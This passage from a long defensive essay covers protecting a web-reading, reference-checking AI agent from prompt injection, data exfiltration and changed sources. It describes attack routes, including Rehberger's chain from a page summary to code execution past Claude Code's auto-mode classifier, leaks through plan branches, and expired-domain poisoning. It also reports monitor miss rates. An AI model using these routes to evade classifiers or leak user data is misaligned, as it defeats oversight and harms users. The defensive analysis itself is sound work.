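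Caching can help too. If the agent asks for the same page twice within a few minutes, the software can return a stored copy, so the site's owner sees only the first request. This has nearly the same effect as forbidding repeat visits, but the agent still gets the page each time. The stored copy may be slightly out of date.

ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode is much stricter. It limits browsing to cached content, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. The owner of a hostile site therefore learns nothing from which page the agent opens. OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* warns that a cached page can still contain an injection and affect the answer. OpenAI also says, in The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*, that data may still leak through connected apps or undiscovered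 techniques.

This protection would make the analyst's work much harder. Cached results may be old or missing, and the mode disables Deep Research and agent mode, according to VPNCentral's *ChatGPT Lockdown Mode Limits Web Access to Reduce Prompt Injection Data Theft*. She would want those features most for checking eighty references. OpenAI considers the mode unnecessary for most users.

Warnings leave the decision to the user. They work best when they are rare and show exactly what data would be sent, as Safe Url is meant to do. A user can recognise her own address at the end of a link, but not data encoded in the sequence of pages the agent opens, such as page 14, then page 3, then page 27, because each link looks harmless. OpenAI, like Costa and colleagues, also worries about approval fatigue. If a fifth of the analyst's references were missing from the crawler's record, she would face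 16 warnings in one job, nearly all of them for harmless pages.

A reference checker has a simpler option, because the reference list already contains most of the addresses it needs. Ordinary software can fetch all eighty pages in list order and save them before the model reads any of them. Neither a hostile page nor the contents of the analyst's private files can then influence these requests. Only one sequence is permitted, so $k$ is 1 and the choice of address leaks $\log_2 1 = 0$ bits.

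Opening links found inside the pages requires a second round of downloads. The software could apply a fixed rule, such as downloading the first PDF that each page links to, so that the model again doesn't choose which links to open. This rule would download some irrelevant files and miss some papers. For the missed papers, the agent could give the analyst one list of further addresses at the end, and she could decide which to open.

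## Which tools should the agent keep while it reads untrusted pages?

If ordinary software saves all eighty pages in advance, a hostile page can't make the agent send data out through a web request. But the analyst's agent still has access to her files and email account while it reads those pages. A tool gate can check each call, but someone must first decide what it should permit. That is difficult because the danger of one tool depends on what else the agent can read and do.

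### Capabilities that are dangerous together

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) lists three capabilities that together let an attacker steal data through an agent: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside world. If any one is missing, the attacker has nothing to steal, no way to instruct the agent, or no way to receive the data. The analyst's agent has all three. Users often assemble the combination without noticing. Willison blames the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools, for encouraging people to mix tools from different suppliers.

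Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) builds on this idea. It allows an agent no more than two of these properties in one session:

- **A:** it processes untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change something or communicate externally.

Meta's rule covers more kinds of harm than Willison's trifecta, which concerns data theft. The trifecta doesn't cover an agent that deletes files on a page's instruction but can't send anything out, while Meta's property C does. When a task needs all three properties, Willison advises users to avoid the combination entirely, while Meta accepts it under supervision, such as human approval.

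The rule's weak point is the pair A and C, which is safe only if "sensitive systems" is defined broadly. Suppose an agent has no private data but can edit a reference library that the analyst's team shares. A hostile page could make it delete entries, and the rule forbids this only if the library counts as sensitive. Meta also says the rule does not prevent misinformation in the agent's answer.

Meta lets an agent change which two properties it has during a session, which suits the analyst. Her agent could first fetch the public sources without access to her files. Software would then switch off the web and email before giving the agent access to her draft and the internal documents. The agent could still check every reference, but she would have to send the results to her co-authors herself. The web and email must stay off for the rest of the session, because the hostile page is still in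 the agent's context and restoring email would give the agent all three properties.

### Giving the agent fewer permissions from the start

The oldest approach is least privilege, which means giving a program only the permissions its job requires. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) explains that a login alone is not enough, because a valid credential may give an agent access to a system but does not establish which actions it is authorised to take there.

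The analyst could give her agent read access to one folder of internal references and let it save email drafts without sending them. The agent could then no longer search the rest of her files for a missing document or contact anyone. These limits don't depend on a model's judgement, and they work well when the job is always the same. A general assistant is harder to restrict this way, because one fixed list of permissions has to cover every task its user might set.

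### Deciding what to do before reading

Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, describe six designs based on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any consequential action. They support the designs with ten case studies, in which they discuss security and usefulness but measure neither. The table applies the designs to reference checking.

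| Design | How it could check references | What a hostile page can still do | What the agent can no longer do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Action selector | A model picks a ready-made command, such as "test every link", and never sees the results | Nothing to the model | Judge whether a source supports a sentence |
| Plan-then-execute | A model lists the steps before opening any page, and software allows only those steps | Change what the table or email contains | Search for a page that has moved, unless the plan includes it |
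| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each page and returns a fixed verdict, and code builds the table | Falsify its own verdict | Compare sources with each other or explain a verdict in prose |
| Dual LLM | A planner calls the tools, while a second model without tools reads the pages | Falsify the second model's answers | Let the planner read a page and decide what to do next |
| Code-then-execute | A model writes a complete program before any page is read | Falsify values that the program uses | Rewrite the program when a page is not as expected |
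| Context minimisation | Software extracts the addresses from the analyst's pasted list and removes the rest of the text | Everything it could do before, since this protects only against text in the user's own message | Consult notes she included in the list |

*Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025) recommends checking a plan against security policies before running it, then keeping it unchanged. But a plan that fixes only the tool names may not help much. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an assistant that has committed to two commands, one that finds files and one that moves them. A planted instruction could make it find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive using only those commands.

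A fixed plan can also leak data through a step the user wanted. The formal analysis *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) confirms that an injection cannot add a tool call to a dual-LLM agent and can only make an answer wrong. But in one of its examples, the model that reads the untrusted text can also read the user's private notes. The injection makes that model quote the notes in a reply, which the plan then sends.

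Labels on the data can stop this leak, but a plan that branches can still leak information through which branch the agent takes. Suppose the analyst's plan opens a publisher's correction form whenever the verdict is "does not support". If the reading model has her whole draft, a hostile page could tell it to return that verdict only if the draft mentions a certain company. The publisher would learn whether it does from whether the agent opened the form.

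Map-reduce is therefore probably the best of the six for this job, provided each reading model receives only one page and the sentence that cites it. The analyst can't compare sources this way, but most of her eighty checks don't require it.

### Writing a policy for each task

A separate policy for each task can be much stricter than one fixed list. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses a language model to write the policy from the user's request. Each rule names a tool and sets conditions on its arguments, and ordinary code blocks any call that no rule allows. For the analyst, the policy might allow the agent to open the eighty listed addresses, read one folder and email two named co-authors.

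The model can propose changes as the agent learns more. If $A(P)$ is the set of calls that policy $P$ allows, a new policy $P'$ takes effect automatically only when

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

A solver, a program that settles logical questions by calculation, checks whether an update would add permissions. If it would, the update needs approval. For example, if reference 14 has moved, the agent can't open the new address until someone approves it. A planted instruction might lead the model to propose emailing a stranger, but that would need approval too.

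On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On ASB, a test set with ten agent scenarios, Progent lowered the attack success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Shi and colleagues report that utility stayed about the same on both. These tests used GPT-4o, an old model, but Progent also cut the rate from 6.8% to 0.5% when the agent ran on Claude Sonnet 4.

Those headline results provide little evidence about the approval rule, because Shi and colleagues set the system to approve every expansion automatically. The protection came from the policies the model wrote. When a person reviewed the initial policy and every expansion, no attacks succeeded. Only 6% of updates on AgentDojo needed approval, so the extra work was small. A task that follows links to unfamiliar sites would presumably need more approvals.

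In the AgentDojo tests, Shi and colleagues also let the agent use non-sensitive, read-only tools freely. A web-reading agent with this set-up should not have free use of its page-fetching tool, since the addresses it requests can leak private data.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticises Progent for covering only tool calls and so not addressing attacks on the agent's text output. It also warns that hostile tool results may lead the update mechanism to loosen the policy. The approval step addresses the second problem only if the person approving looks carefully.

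*DRIFT* (2025), which Ma and colleagues compared with ROPE, relies more heavily on models. It predicts a plan, has another model judge departures from it, and writes a checklist for the arguments of the tool calls. Another component clears the agent's memory of instructions that conflict with the user's request, so they can't influence later steps.

The analyst's agent could follow reference 14 to its new address without asking her if the judging model agreed. But an attacker can try to fool that model. In Ma and colleagues' tests of DRIFT, adaptive attacks succeeded far more often than fixed ones against one of the agent models. DRIFT also sharply reduced task completion.

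### Do people read confirmation prompts?

Meta's rule and Progent both fall back on human approval. The best evidence on how well this works comes from Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), which reports that Claude Code users approve 97% of requests to carry out a single action. That figure alone proves little, because most such requests are harmless.

Anthropic commissioned an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. During a coding session, the software replaced one ordinary request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. If the analyst had to approve each page separately, she would reach 50 requests with thirty references still to check.

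Approval fatigue would produce the decline seen during a session. There are two reasons to be cautious about the result, though neither readily explains that decline. The testers worked in a test environment with nothing of their own at risk, so they may have been less careful than people protecting their own files. Anthropic also had a reason to publicise the result, since it was introducing an automatic alternative.

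People seem to pay more attention to plans. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it presents, but 3% of single actions. Some presumably reject a plan because they want the work done differently, not because they noticed a danger, but they are at least reading it. The analyst's software could ask her to approve the whole list of steps at the start, and then the finished email. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that an email can carry data in characters that don't appear on the screen, so even a careful reviewer can miss it.

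Anthropic's alternative, auto mode, has a classifier approve or block actions. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not the content of web pages, so a page can't address it directly. The company tested it on three sets of actions:

| Test set | Classifier's error rate |
|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic staff | Blocked 0.4% of harmless calls |
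| 52 real actions that went beyond what the user wanted | Missed 17% |
| 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out | Missed 5.7% |

The second set had only 52 actions, so the true miss rate could be between about 9% and 30%. In the experiment with paid testers, the classifier blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, far more than people did. Anthropic still recommends careful human review for high-stakes infrastructure.

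The company also cites a test in which none of 720 prompt injection attempts succeeded against its newest models in auto mode. This is weak evidence for the classifier, because the average success rate was only 0.09% against the same models without it. The testing company had also optimised the attacks against an older model rather than adapting them to auto mode.

### When a summary ends in code execution

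In August 2026, Rehberger demonstrated an attack on Claude Code in auto mode that began with a request to summarise a web page. According to The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code*, the site made the agent's usual page-reading tool fail, so the agent used the terminal and downloaded an archive of files. It refused to run a program in the archive and wrote its own to decode the contents. The agent's program loaded another of the attacker's files, which ran code on the user's computer.

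Rehberger tried three variants of the attack five times each. Crosley reports in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* that the variants succeeded three, three and four times. These results show that the attack can work, but there were too few runs to give more than a rough idea of how often.

Anthropic told Rehberger that the behaviour was working as designed. In his paraphrase, the company called auto mode "a convenience feature backed by a best-effort classifier, not a security guarantee". This is a fair description of a classifier. Users may struggle to reconcile it with Anthropic's claim that auto mode is safer than manual approval, although both could be true if people approve nearly every action when asked.

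Willison (2026) first treated the attack as prompt injection, then accepted a reader's correction that the model had never followed a malicious instruction. The agent made choices that each looked reasonable in a setting the attacker had arranged, so a detector for planted instructions might have found nothing.

Willison agrees with Rehberger that coding agents should run in a sandbox, an isolated environment with limited network access and none of the user's credentials. It would be easier for the analyst to remove the terminal, since her agent doesn't need one to read a page. If the page-reading tool failed, the agent would report that it couldn't open the source. She would have to open some unusual file formats herself.

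### Switching capabilities off across a product

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode offers similar restrictions to people who don't build their own agents. It limits ChatGPT's browsing to cached pages, stops ChatGPT from downloading files for data analysis, and prevents users from giving network access to code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace. In Meta's terms, ChatGPT keeps properties A and B but loses much of C.

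Willison (2026) likes the design because fixed software enforces the limits, so an attacker can't remove them by manipulating the model. He also infers that ChatGPT's default settings don't provide robust protection against a determined attempt to steal data.

The mode has gaps that a user could easily miss. According to OpenAI, it doesn't affect network access in Codex, the company's coding agent, and users of personal accounts can turn it off for a single chat. In workspaces managed by an organisation, connected apps do not all switch off automatically. OpenAI advises administrators not to let even a trusted app write data unless they are sure an attacker couldn't see the result.

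The analyst could still use Lockdown Mode by saving the eighty pages and uploading them with her draft. ChatGPT could compare the two, but it couldn't fetch a missing source from the live web. She would also have to send the table to her co-authors herself, unless her organisation had left an email app enabled.

### Is a permitted tool still the same tool?

A tool gate usually identifies a tool by its name, but the supplier can change the tool without changing its name. The supplier could add instructions for the model to the tool's description, or change what the tool does while leaving the description the same.

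A developer can use pinning to detect changes to a tool's description. The developer stores a cryptographic hash of the tool's definition when approving it, and blocks the tool if the hash later differs. Pinning doesn't detect a change in the tool's behaviour if the definition stays the same.

Pinning a version number doesn't guarantee stable behaviour either. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *ProbeID*, sent the same requests to 59 tools on 16 public MCP servers eleven times over eleven weeks. Seven tools changed their responses although their version numbers stayed the same:

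- Three weather tools returned updated content.
- One tool that recommends Amazon cloud documentation drifted until its answers no longer resembled the originals.
- Three tools gave different error messages after the researchers reinstalled them, because a software library they depend on had changed.

None of these changes was evidence of malice. A developer who blocked every tool whose answers changed would therefore block some useful ones.

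ProbeID checks a tool's behaviour directly. When a developer approves a tool, ProbeID sends it a set of test inputs and stores the answers, after removing details that vary harmlessly, such as timestamps. Before the agent uses the tool again, ProbeID sends a secret random selection of the same inputs and compares the new answers with the stored ones. It refuses the tool if the answers differ too much.

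A small change in behaviour is easy to miss. If a tool now gives different answers to a share $\phi$ of inputs, the chance that $m$ random tests all miss the change is

$$(1-\phi)^m$$

If 5% of answers have changed, 32 tests miss the change 19% of the time and 90 tests about 1% of the time.

The researchers also deliberately replaced some of an agent's tools with altered versions. The agent received at least one wrong value in 15 of 16 tasks without ProbeID and in 9 with it. The remaining errors came from two tools whose test inputs never triggered the altered behaviour. Every task was scored as successful with or without ProbeID, so a developer who looked only at task success would not have noticed the wrong values. A single ProbeID check took up to 512 test calls.

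The analyst's page-fetching tool would be awkward to test this way, because web pages change for ordinary reasons. Her software could fetch fixed pages from a server she controls and check that the text arrives intact. But a tool could return every page correctly and still send a copy of her data elsewhere, which comparing responses would not reveal. She could prevent that by running the tool on her own machine and restricting its network connections to the sites in her reference list, but she can't restrict the connections of a tool that runs on a stranger's server.

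## What does a matching checksum prove about a cited page?

URL and tool gates limit what a hostile page can make the agent do, but they don't show whether the page behind reference 14 has changed since the analyst cited it. Ordinary software can check this if she recorded a checksum at the time. Pinning a tool's definition works the same way.

A matching checksum proves only that the agent received exactly the bytes originally recorded, though it proves this with near certainty. Mismatches are harder to interpret because they are common, mostly innocent, and look the same whether an advertiser or an attacker caused them.

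### How the check works

The checksum has to be a cryptographic hash. SHA-256, a common choice, always produces 256 bits, usually written as 64 characters, however long the file is. Even a small change to the text gives an unrelated value:

| Text | First eight characters of the SHA-256 hash |
|---|---|
| `hello world` | `b94d27b9` |
| `Hello World` | `a591a6d4` |

To check a citation, the software does the following:

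1. When the analyst cites a page, her software fetches its content $x$ and records the address, the time and the hash $h = H(x)$.
2. When the agent checks the reference, its software fetches the address again and receives $x'$.
3. The software computes $H(x')$ and reports a match only if $H(x') = h$.

An attacker would need about $2^{256}$ guesses to replace the page without changing its SHA-256 hash, far more than any computer could make. Older checksums such as CRC-32 catch accidental damage during storage or transmission, but they don't protect against deliberate replacement, because anyone can give an altered file the expected CRC-32 value by adjusting four of its bytes.

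MD5, an older cryptographic hash, is also unsuitable. *Trainwreck* (2023), a paper on sabotaged training data, recommends SHA-256 or SHA-512 because an attacker may be able to make altered data match an MD5 hash. In practical attacks on MD5, the attacker creates both of the files that share a hash, so the main danger is a hostile publisher, who could prepare a harmless page for the analyst to cite and a malicious one to replace it with later.

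### What a match leaves open

A page may already contain planted instructions when its checksum is recorded. Many of the pages on which Khodayari and colleagues found such instructions already contained an injection about a year earlier. A checksum recorded then would have included the injection, and it would still match if the page hadn't changed.

A matching checksum doesn't prove that a page's claims are true, because a false page also matches its own hash. *Proof-Gated Publication* (2026), which deals with copying data between databases, tests a similar case in which software misreads the source and copies the wrong data faithfully. The comparison passes, but an independent count of the rows at the source reveals the error. An analyst can similarly check a claim against a second source.

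The analyst and the agent may read different words even when their files are identical and the hashes match. *What Users See Is Not What Models Read* (2026) describes PDF files whose visible text differs from the text that software extracts, and reports that many extraction tools and AI services are vulnerable. The analyst reads the visible text on her screen, while the agent receives the extracted text. To catch this, software would have to compare the extracted text with an image of the page.

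The result also depends on who supplies the reference hash. Aloufi and Alsewari (2021) point out in *Toward Efficient Web Publishing with Provenance of Information Using Trusty URIs* that someone who changes a page can easily update its hash too. A hash that the website sends with the page can therefore reveal transmission errors, but not a dishonest website. *Proof-Gated Publication* recommends a signed reference value from a system that whoever wrote the copy does not control.

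The analyst's own reference list is a good place for the hash, provided the agent can't edit the list. If she saved the page with her ordinary browser, a mismatch with the agent's later copy may reveal that the site shows agents a different version. But a cloaking site could go undetected if an agent saved the original page, because the site could serve the same hostile version both times and the hashes would match.

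### Buying the address of somebody else's source

Owners rent domain names for a limited period. If they stop paying, anyone can register the name and decide what every old address on it returns. Carlini, Jagielski and colleagues (2023) showed in *Poisoning Web-Scale Training Datasets is Practical* that this is a cheap way to replace content that other people rely on.

Researchers studied ten large sets of images for training AI models. To avoid storage costs and legal problems, the maintainers of such sets publish only a list of addresses with captions or labels, and each user downloads the images from the original sites. In what the researchers call split-view poisoning, a user receives a different image from the one the maintainer saw at the same address. A reference list has the same weakness, because it pairs each address with a sentence that someone wrote after reading an earlier version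 of the page.

At 2023 prices, an attacker could have controlled at least 0.01% of any of the ten sets for \$60 a year or less. Older sets had a larger share of their images on expired domains, from 0.71% for a set published in 2021 to 6.48% for one published in 2010. On the day one set was published, 0.1% of its images were already on expired domains that were for sale, because collecting the addresses had taken nearly a year.

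Carlini and colleagues bought six expired domains per dataset, logged the requests and answered each one with an error. Over six months, they counted more than 800 downloads that they could have poisoned. In a simulation on their own copy of a 400-million-image dataset, replacing 1,000 images made the trained model misclassify a chosen image 60% of the time. They found no sign that anyone had carried out such an attack.

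An attacker who wants to mislead readers of one report needs only one of its references. If each of the analyst's eighty references had a 1% chance of being on an expired domain, independently of the others, the chance of at least one would be

$$1 - 0.99^{80} \approx 55\%$$

The 1% figure is close to the share for an image set published in 2018. References to journals and government sites probably last longer, and several references may share a domain, so the true chance could be much lower. The researchers obtained valid security certificates for the domains they bought, so the browser's padlock would not have revealed the change of owner.

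### What a new owner inherits

An attacker who takes over a domain can gain more than its address. *Zombies in Alternate Realities* (Thottungal Valapu, Jonker and Sommese, 2026) studied three systems that use control of a domain as proof of identity. It found records that had outlived the domain ownership they were based on in about 3% of web certificates for new domains, 24% of one type of link between domains and cryptocurrency wallets, and 15% of the publisher names on Maven Central, a large store of Java software.

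Maven Central is the most worrying case, because anyone who proves control of a domain can claim the right to publish under its name. Someone who buys a lapsed domain could then release a hostile update to software that people have trusted for years, although they would first have to pass a manual review. The researchers found 214 publisher names that had issued new versions after someone re-registered the domain. They did not compare the software or the keys that signed it, so the finding shows that these names were vulnerable but not that anyone attacked them. Some of the new versions may have come from the original publishers, who can keep their accounts after losing the domain.

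Criminals have exploited expired domains elsewhere. *What Gets Measured Gets Managed* (2025) cites a campaign in which attackers re-registered the domain of a visitor-counting service that had closed in 2014. More than 40 online shops still loaded the service's script, which the attackers used to steal customers' card details.

The same paper proposes blocking domains registered after a chosen date, and software could apply a similar rule to citations. If public records show that a domain was registered after the citation was made, the domain has lapsed and someone has registered it again. This check needs no hash, so it also works on old references. It won't detect a hacked site or the sale of a domain that never lapsed, and it will sometimes flag a domain whose owner forgot to renew it and then registered it again.

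### The hash defence and its cost

Carlini and colleagues propose preventing split-view poisoning by having maintainers publish a SHA-256 hash for every image and having downloaders discard any image that doesn't match. This stops the attack completely if the hashes are genuine and the maintainer computed them before the attack.

To measure how many available images a strict hash check would discard, they took an original 2018 download of 3.3 million images and fetched the same addresses again in 2023. About 2.9 million images were still online, but only 1.1 million matched their original hashes. The check would therefore have discarded 1.8 million available images, or 62% of those still online.

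Almost none of those changes seem to have been attacks. The researchers found one domain in this set that had changed both owner and content, and it belonged to a speculator who showed advertisements. Common causes of a mismatch include resizing an image or saving it in another format.

A perceptual hash, which stays the same when an image changes only slightly, would accept more of these images. But an attacker can adjust a poisoned image until its perceptual hash matches the original's, so using one gives up most of the security. Text similarity measures would probably have the same weakness, since inserting "not" barely changes a page but can reverse its meaning.

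After the researchers contacted the maintainers, six of the ten datasets began to offer SHA-256 hashes of their images. The researchers also added an optional check to img2dataset, the tool that made about three quarters of the requests to their domains. But publishing hashes achieves little if users don't check them. Two older datasets already had hashes, but for each dataset, only one of the six most popular download scripts could verify them. Three large datasets published after the paper first appeared had no hashes.

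Hashes also don't protect against the researchers' second attack, frontrunning, in which someone alters a page just before it is due to be copied. Wikipedia copies its articles in a predictable order, and the researchers estimated that an attacker could get edits into the copies of 6.5% of English articles before editors reversed them. A hash of such a copy would match the attacker's version. An ordinary citation is safer from this attack because an attacker rarely knows when an author will save a page.

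### How often do cited pages change?

Sielinski (2026), in *Quantifying Uncertainty in AI Visibility*, recorded SHA-256 hashes of the readable text on pages cited by three AI search services, once a day for nine days. Among the most frequently cited sites, most showed no change from one day to the next, but a few, including runnersworld.com on one service, had a different hash at every comparison. Sielinski suggests timestamps, session codes and advertising slots as causes. The study covered only three consumer topics and left out pages that blocked its software, but it shows that on some sites even a hash of the readable text can stop matching every day.

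Over longer periods, many apparent changes to a page are failures to fetch it. *When 200 OK Is Not an Answer* (2026) re-fetched sources cited in ExpertQA, a set of AI answers to experts' questions. Servers send the code "200 OK" to report success, but it often accompanies an error message or an empty page. Based on status codes alone, 11.8% of the addresses were dead. Including error, substitute and parked pages that reported success, 16.0% no longer served the cited content.

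If one counts every reported success as a real page, 274 sources seemed to have drifted away from what they were cited for. But 217 of these (79%) had not returned a usable page:

| What the server returned | Cases |
|---|---|
| An error page, a substitute or a parked domain | 96 |
| A block or a test for robots | 73 |
| An empty shell or part of a page | 48 |
| A usable page | 57 |

The split is approximate because an automatic method labelled these responses. Even so, an agent that treated every mismatch as a publisher's edit would have been wrong about most of these sources. At the 16% rate, about 13 of the analyst's eighty references would no longer lead to the cited content.

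### Hashing less than the whole page

Software can avoid many harmless mismatches by hashing only the part that matters. Each choice also determines which hostile changes can escape notice:

| What the software hashes | Harmless changes that still match | Hostile changes that can still match |
|---|---|---|
| Whole file | None | None |
| Readable text | New layout, resized images | Altered images, or text that the extractor drops |
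| Quoted passage | Anything elsewhere on the page | A retraction notice or planted instruction elsewhere |
| Canonical form | Differences that the rules ignore | Differences that the rules should not ignore |

The quoted passage is probably the best basis for checking a reference. If the analyst saved the passage, software can search the new page for it. A hash is useful when she can't publish the passage, for instance because of copyright. The software then needs the passage's length so it can hash every stretch of that length on the new page and look for a match.

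Even when a cited passage matches its checksum, the rest of the page may contain something important or harmful. The publisher may have added a retraction notice at the top, or an attacker may have added an instruction at the bottom. If the software gives the agent only the matching passage, the agent won't see the instruction, but it will also miss the retraction notice. A simple compromise is to have a separate model without tools read the full page and choose from a fixed set of answers to report whether it contains a correction or retraction.

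### When different bytes contain the same data

Canonicalisation means reducing a file to a standard form before hashing it. It is easiest for structured data, such as a table of measurements that one agent passes to another. In JSON, a common text format for data, `34` and `34.0` are the same number but give different hashes without canonicalisation.

Gao and Clark (2026), in *Same Data, Different Bytes*, propose rules for standardising JSON before hashing it. Their software reads every number as an exact decimal and converts different encodings of the same character, such as an accented letter, to one form. It then writes the data in a standard order and format, reads it back to check that no number has changed, and computes the SHA-256 hash. Reordering a list still changes the hash, as does replacing the number 7 with the text "7". If a number would lose precision, the software reports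 that it can't process the data.

Gao and Clark tested this on 36 sets of data with six models, three from OpenAI's GPT-5.6 family and three from Anthropic's Claude 5.5 family. An agent received a forwarded copy and had to check it against the data owner's record before answering a question. In one scenario the copy contained the same data in a different form, in another someone had altered the data, and in the third the agent couldn't access the owner's record. Each combination ran three times. The table shows how often the agent reached the expected decision:

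| Scenario and expected decision | General tools only | With an ordinary checksum | With the canonical hash |
|---|---|---|---|
| Same data in another form: accept | 18.4% | 28.5% | 98.8% |
| Altered data: reject | 65.9% | 93.8% | 97.4% |
| Owner's record unavailable: unable to verify | 99.2% | 99.5% | 99.5% |

The large gain in the first row overstates the advantage of the canonical hash. The researchers chose rewritings that their rules treat as equivalent, so the canonical hash was bound to match. Claude Opus 5.5 accepted none of the rewritten data with the ordinary checksum, but it was reasonable to refuse data that failed the only available check.

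Models don't always act on the result of a check. With the ordinary checksum, GPT-5.6 Luna properly rejected altered data only 79.6% of the time. Even with the canonical hash, some agents refused data that matched or failed to reject data that didn't. It would be safer for ordinary software to withhold data that fails the check. The tests used selected changes to JSON files in a small network, so they don't show how well canonicalisation works on web pages.

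### A hostile change that canonicalisation hides

Suppose a developer wants to ignore minor edits to web pages, so the software converts the text to lower case and removes punctuation before hashing it. An attacker then changes a medical page:

| Version | Text on the page | Text that the software hashes |
|---|---|---|
| Cited | `Give 1.5 mg daily.` | `give 15 mg daily` |
| Altered | `Give 15 mg daily.` | `give 15 mg daily` |

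The hashes match even though the dose is ten times higher. Gao and Clark's rules would detect this change, but they treat `21.5` and `21.500` as equal, and the extra zeros may indicate to a scientist how precise a measurement was. Gao and Clark advise developers to choose rules that preserve the distinctions the task needs.

A matching checksum can also fail to reveal tampering if the software hashes one version of the page and the model reads another. For example, if the hash leaves out invisible text but the agent's text extractor keeps it, an attacker could add a hidden instruction without causing a mismatch. The model should therefore receive exactly the text that the software hashed.

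Hashing each paragraph separately and adding up the hashes is also risky, although it would conveniently ignore changes in paragraph order. *Proof-Gated Publication* describes an attack on the same method applied to rows of data, in which someone replaces two rows with one that contributes the same amount to the total. Its remedy is to include a secret key in each hash, so that the attacker can't calculate the total in advance.

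### Addresses that contain the hash

If the address itself contains the hash, anyone who has the address can check the file. Kuhn and Dumontier (2014), in *Trusty URIs*, proposed addresses of this kind. *Knowledge Graphs Evolution and Preservation* (2020) gives an example:

`http://example.org/r1.RAcbjcRIQozo2wBMq4WcCYkFAjRz0AX-Ux3PquZZrC68s`

The letters `RA` identify the hashing method, and the remaining 43 characters are the hash. Each character carries six bits, so 43 are just enough for a 256-bit value. For some structured data, the method hashes the meaning rather than the bytes, so the same data in another format keeps its address.

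Addresses that contain a file's hash, such as Trusty URIs, can protect a whole chain of citations. If a file cites its sources by Trusty URI, the file contains their hashes, so its own hash covers them too. The agent can also accept a copy from any server, because it can check the copy against the hash. Content-addressed storage systems look up files by hash alone, without naming a server.

A hash in the address does not show that the address is the right one. *Making Digital Artifacts on the Web Verifiable and Reliable* (2015) notes that someone can supply a manipulated file under a different Trusty URI. The analyst still has to get the address from a trustworthy place, and someone has to keep a copy of the file. A corrected version also gets a new address, so the old citation still leads to the uncorrected one.

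Browsers offer a similar check called subresource integrity. A web developer who loads a script from another site can put the script's expected hash in the page, and the browser won't run the script if its hash differs. This check would have stopped the attack on the online shops if they had recorded a hash of the original script. But it covers only files that a page loads, such as scripts and style sheets, not the pages it links to, so an agent that follows citations needs its own software to compare hashes.

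### What a publisher's signature adds

A publisher can sign a page with a private key, and readers can verify the signature with the matching public key. If the publisher corrects the page, they can sign the new version, whereas a stored hash would no longer match. Signing also protects against someone buying an expired domain, because the buyer doesn't receive the private key. Thottungal Valapu and colleagues recommend this kind of separation, in which controlling a domain isn't enough by itself to change what people have linked to it.

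The protection a signature gives depends on how the reader obtained the public key. If the agent fetches the key from the same domain each time, a new owner of the domain can supply a new key and sign everything with it. The analyst would have to record the key when she cites the page, as she would a hash. Few ordinary web pages are signed, so signatures remain mostly an option for software and official data.

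A valid signature doesn't prove that everyone received the same page. *Trustworthy and Confidential SBOM Exchange* (2025) considers a supplier who gives different customers different lists of a product's components. It suggests publishing a signed hash of each list in a public log, where customers can compare what they received. A public log of page hashes could similarly expose cloaking if publishers took part.

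### What should the agent do about a mismatch?

A mismatch tells the agent that its earlier evidence has changed, but not whether the analyst's sentence is wrong. Hsu, Chi and Everett (2026), in *EA-Graph*, deal with a similar problem in coding agents, which often rely on notes about what they checked in an earlier session. Their system stores each conclusion with a hash of the exact values and code that supported it. When the underlying material changes, the agent sorts its old conclusions into three groups:

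- **Unaffected:** the material behind the conclusion is the same.
- **Affected:** the material has changed, and the agent can examine the new version.
- **Unprovable:** the material has changed, and the new version is unavailable.

When the support for a conclusion changes, the system withdraws the conclusion rather than attaching a warning, which would be easy to ignore. It accepts "unprovable" as a final answer, so the agent doesn't have to guess. It also keeps the last verified version of the work, since losing the proof doesn't show that the work was wrong.

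Hsu and colleagues tested this on seven artificial software projects, each with 96 functions to classify after an update. They compared the hashed records with ordinary written notes and with no notes, using two Claude models, for 42 sessions in all. The scores are medians on a scale from 0 to 1 that penalises both missed changes and false alarms:

| Model | Hashed records | Written notes | No notes |
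|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 1.000 | 0.270 | 0.286 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 1.000 | 0.971 | 1.000 |

The smaller model clearly benefited. The larger one usually worked out the changes without help, so the test couldn't show a significant advantage. In one session with Haiku, the system produced the correct list of changes, but the model rejected most of them in its reasoning and scored 0.364. This is another reason to let software withdraw outdated conclusions automatically.

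The projects also show the benefit of hashing small pieces, since checking whole files would have flagged about 88 of the 96 functions when only about 17 had been affected. But a conclusion can wrongly pass the check if the record omits something the conclusion depends on, much as a quotation can still match after a retraction notice is added to the page. The projects were artificial and each combination ran only once, so they are limited evidence about web pages.

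Applied to citations, the three outcomes suggest the following procedure after a mismatch:

1. The software checks whether it received a usable page. If it received an error, a block or an empty shell, it tries again later, and then reports the current page as unprovable.
2. It compares the domain's registration date with the date of citation. If someone has re-registered the domain since, it keeps the page away from the agent and tells the analyst.
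3. It looks for the quoted passage. If the passage is still there and the page contains no correction or retraction, the reference is unaffected.
4. If the passage has changed or disappeared, the reference is affected. The agent judges the new text and reports that its verdict applies to the new version.

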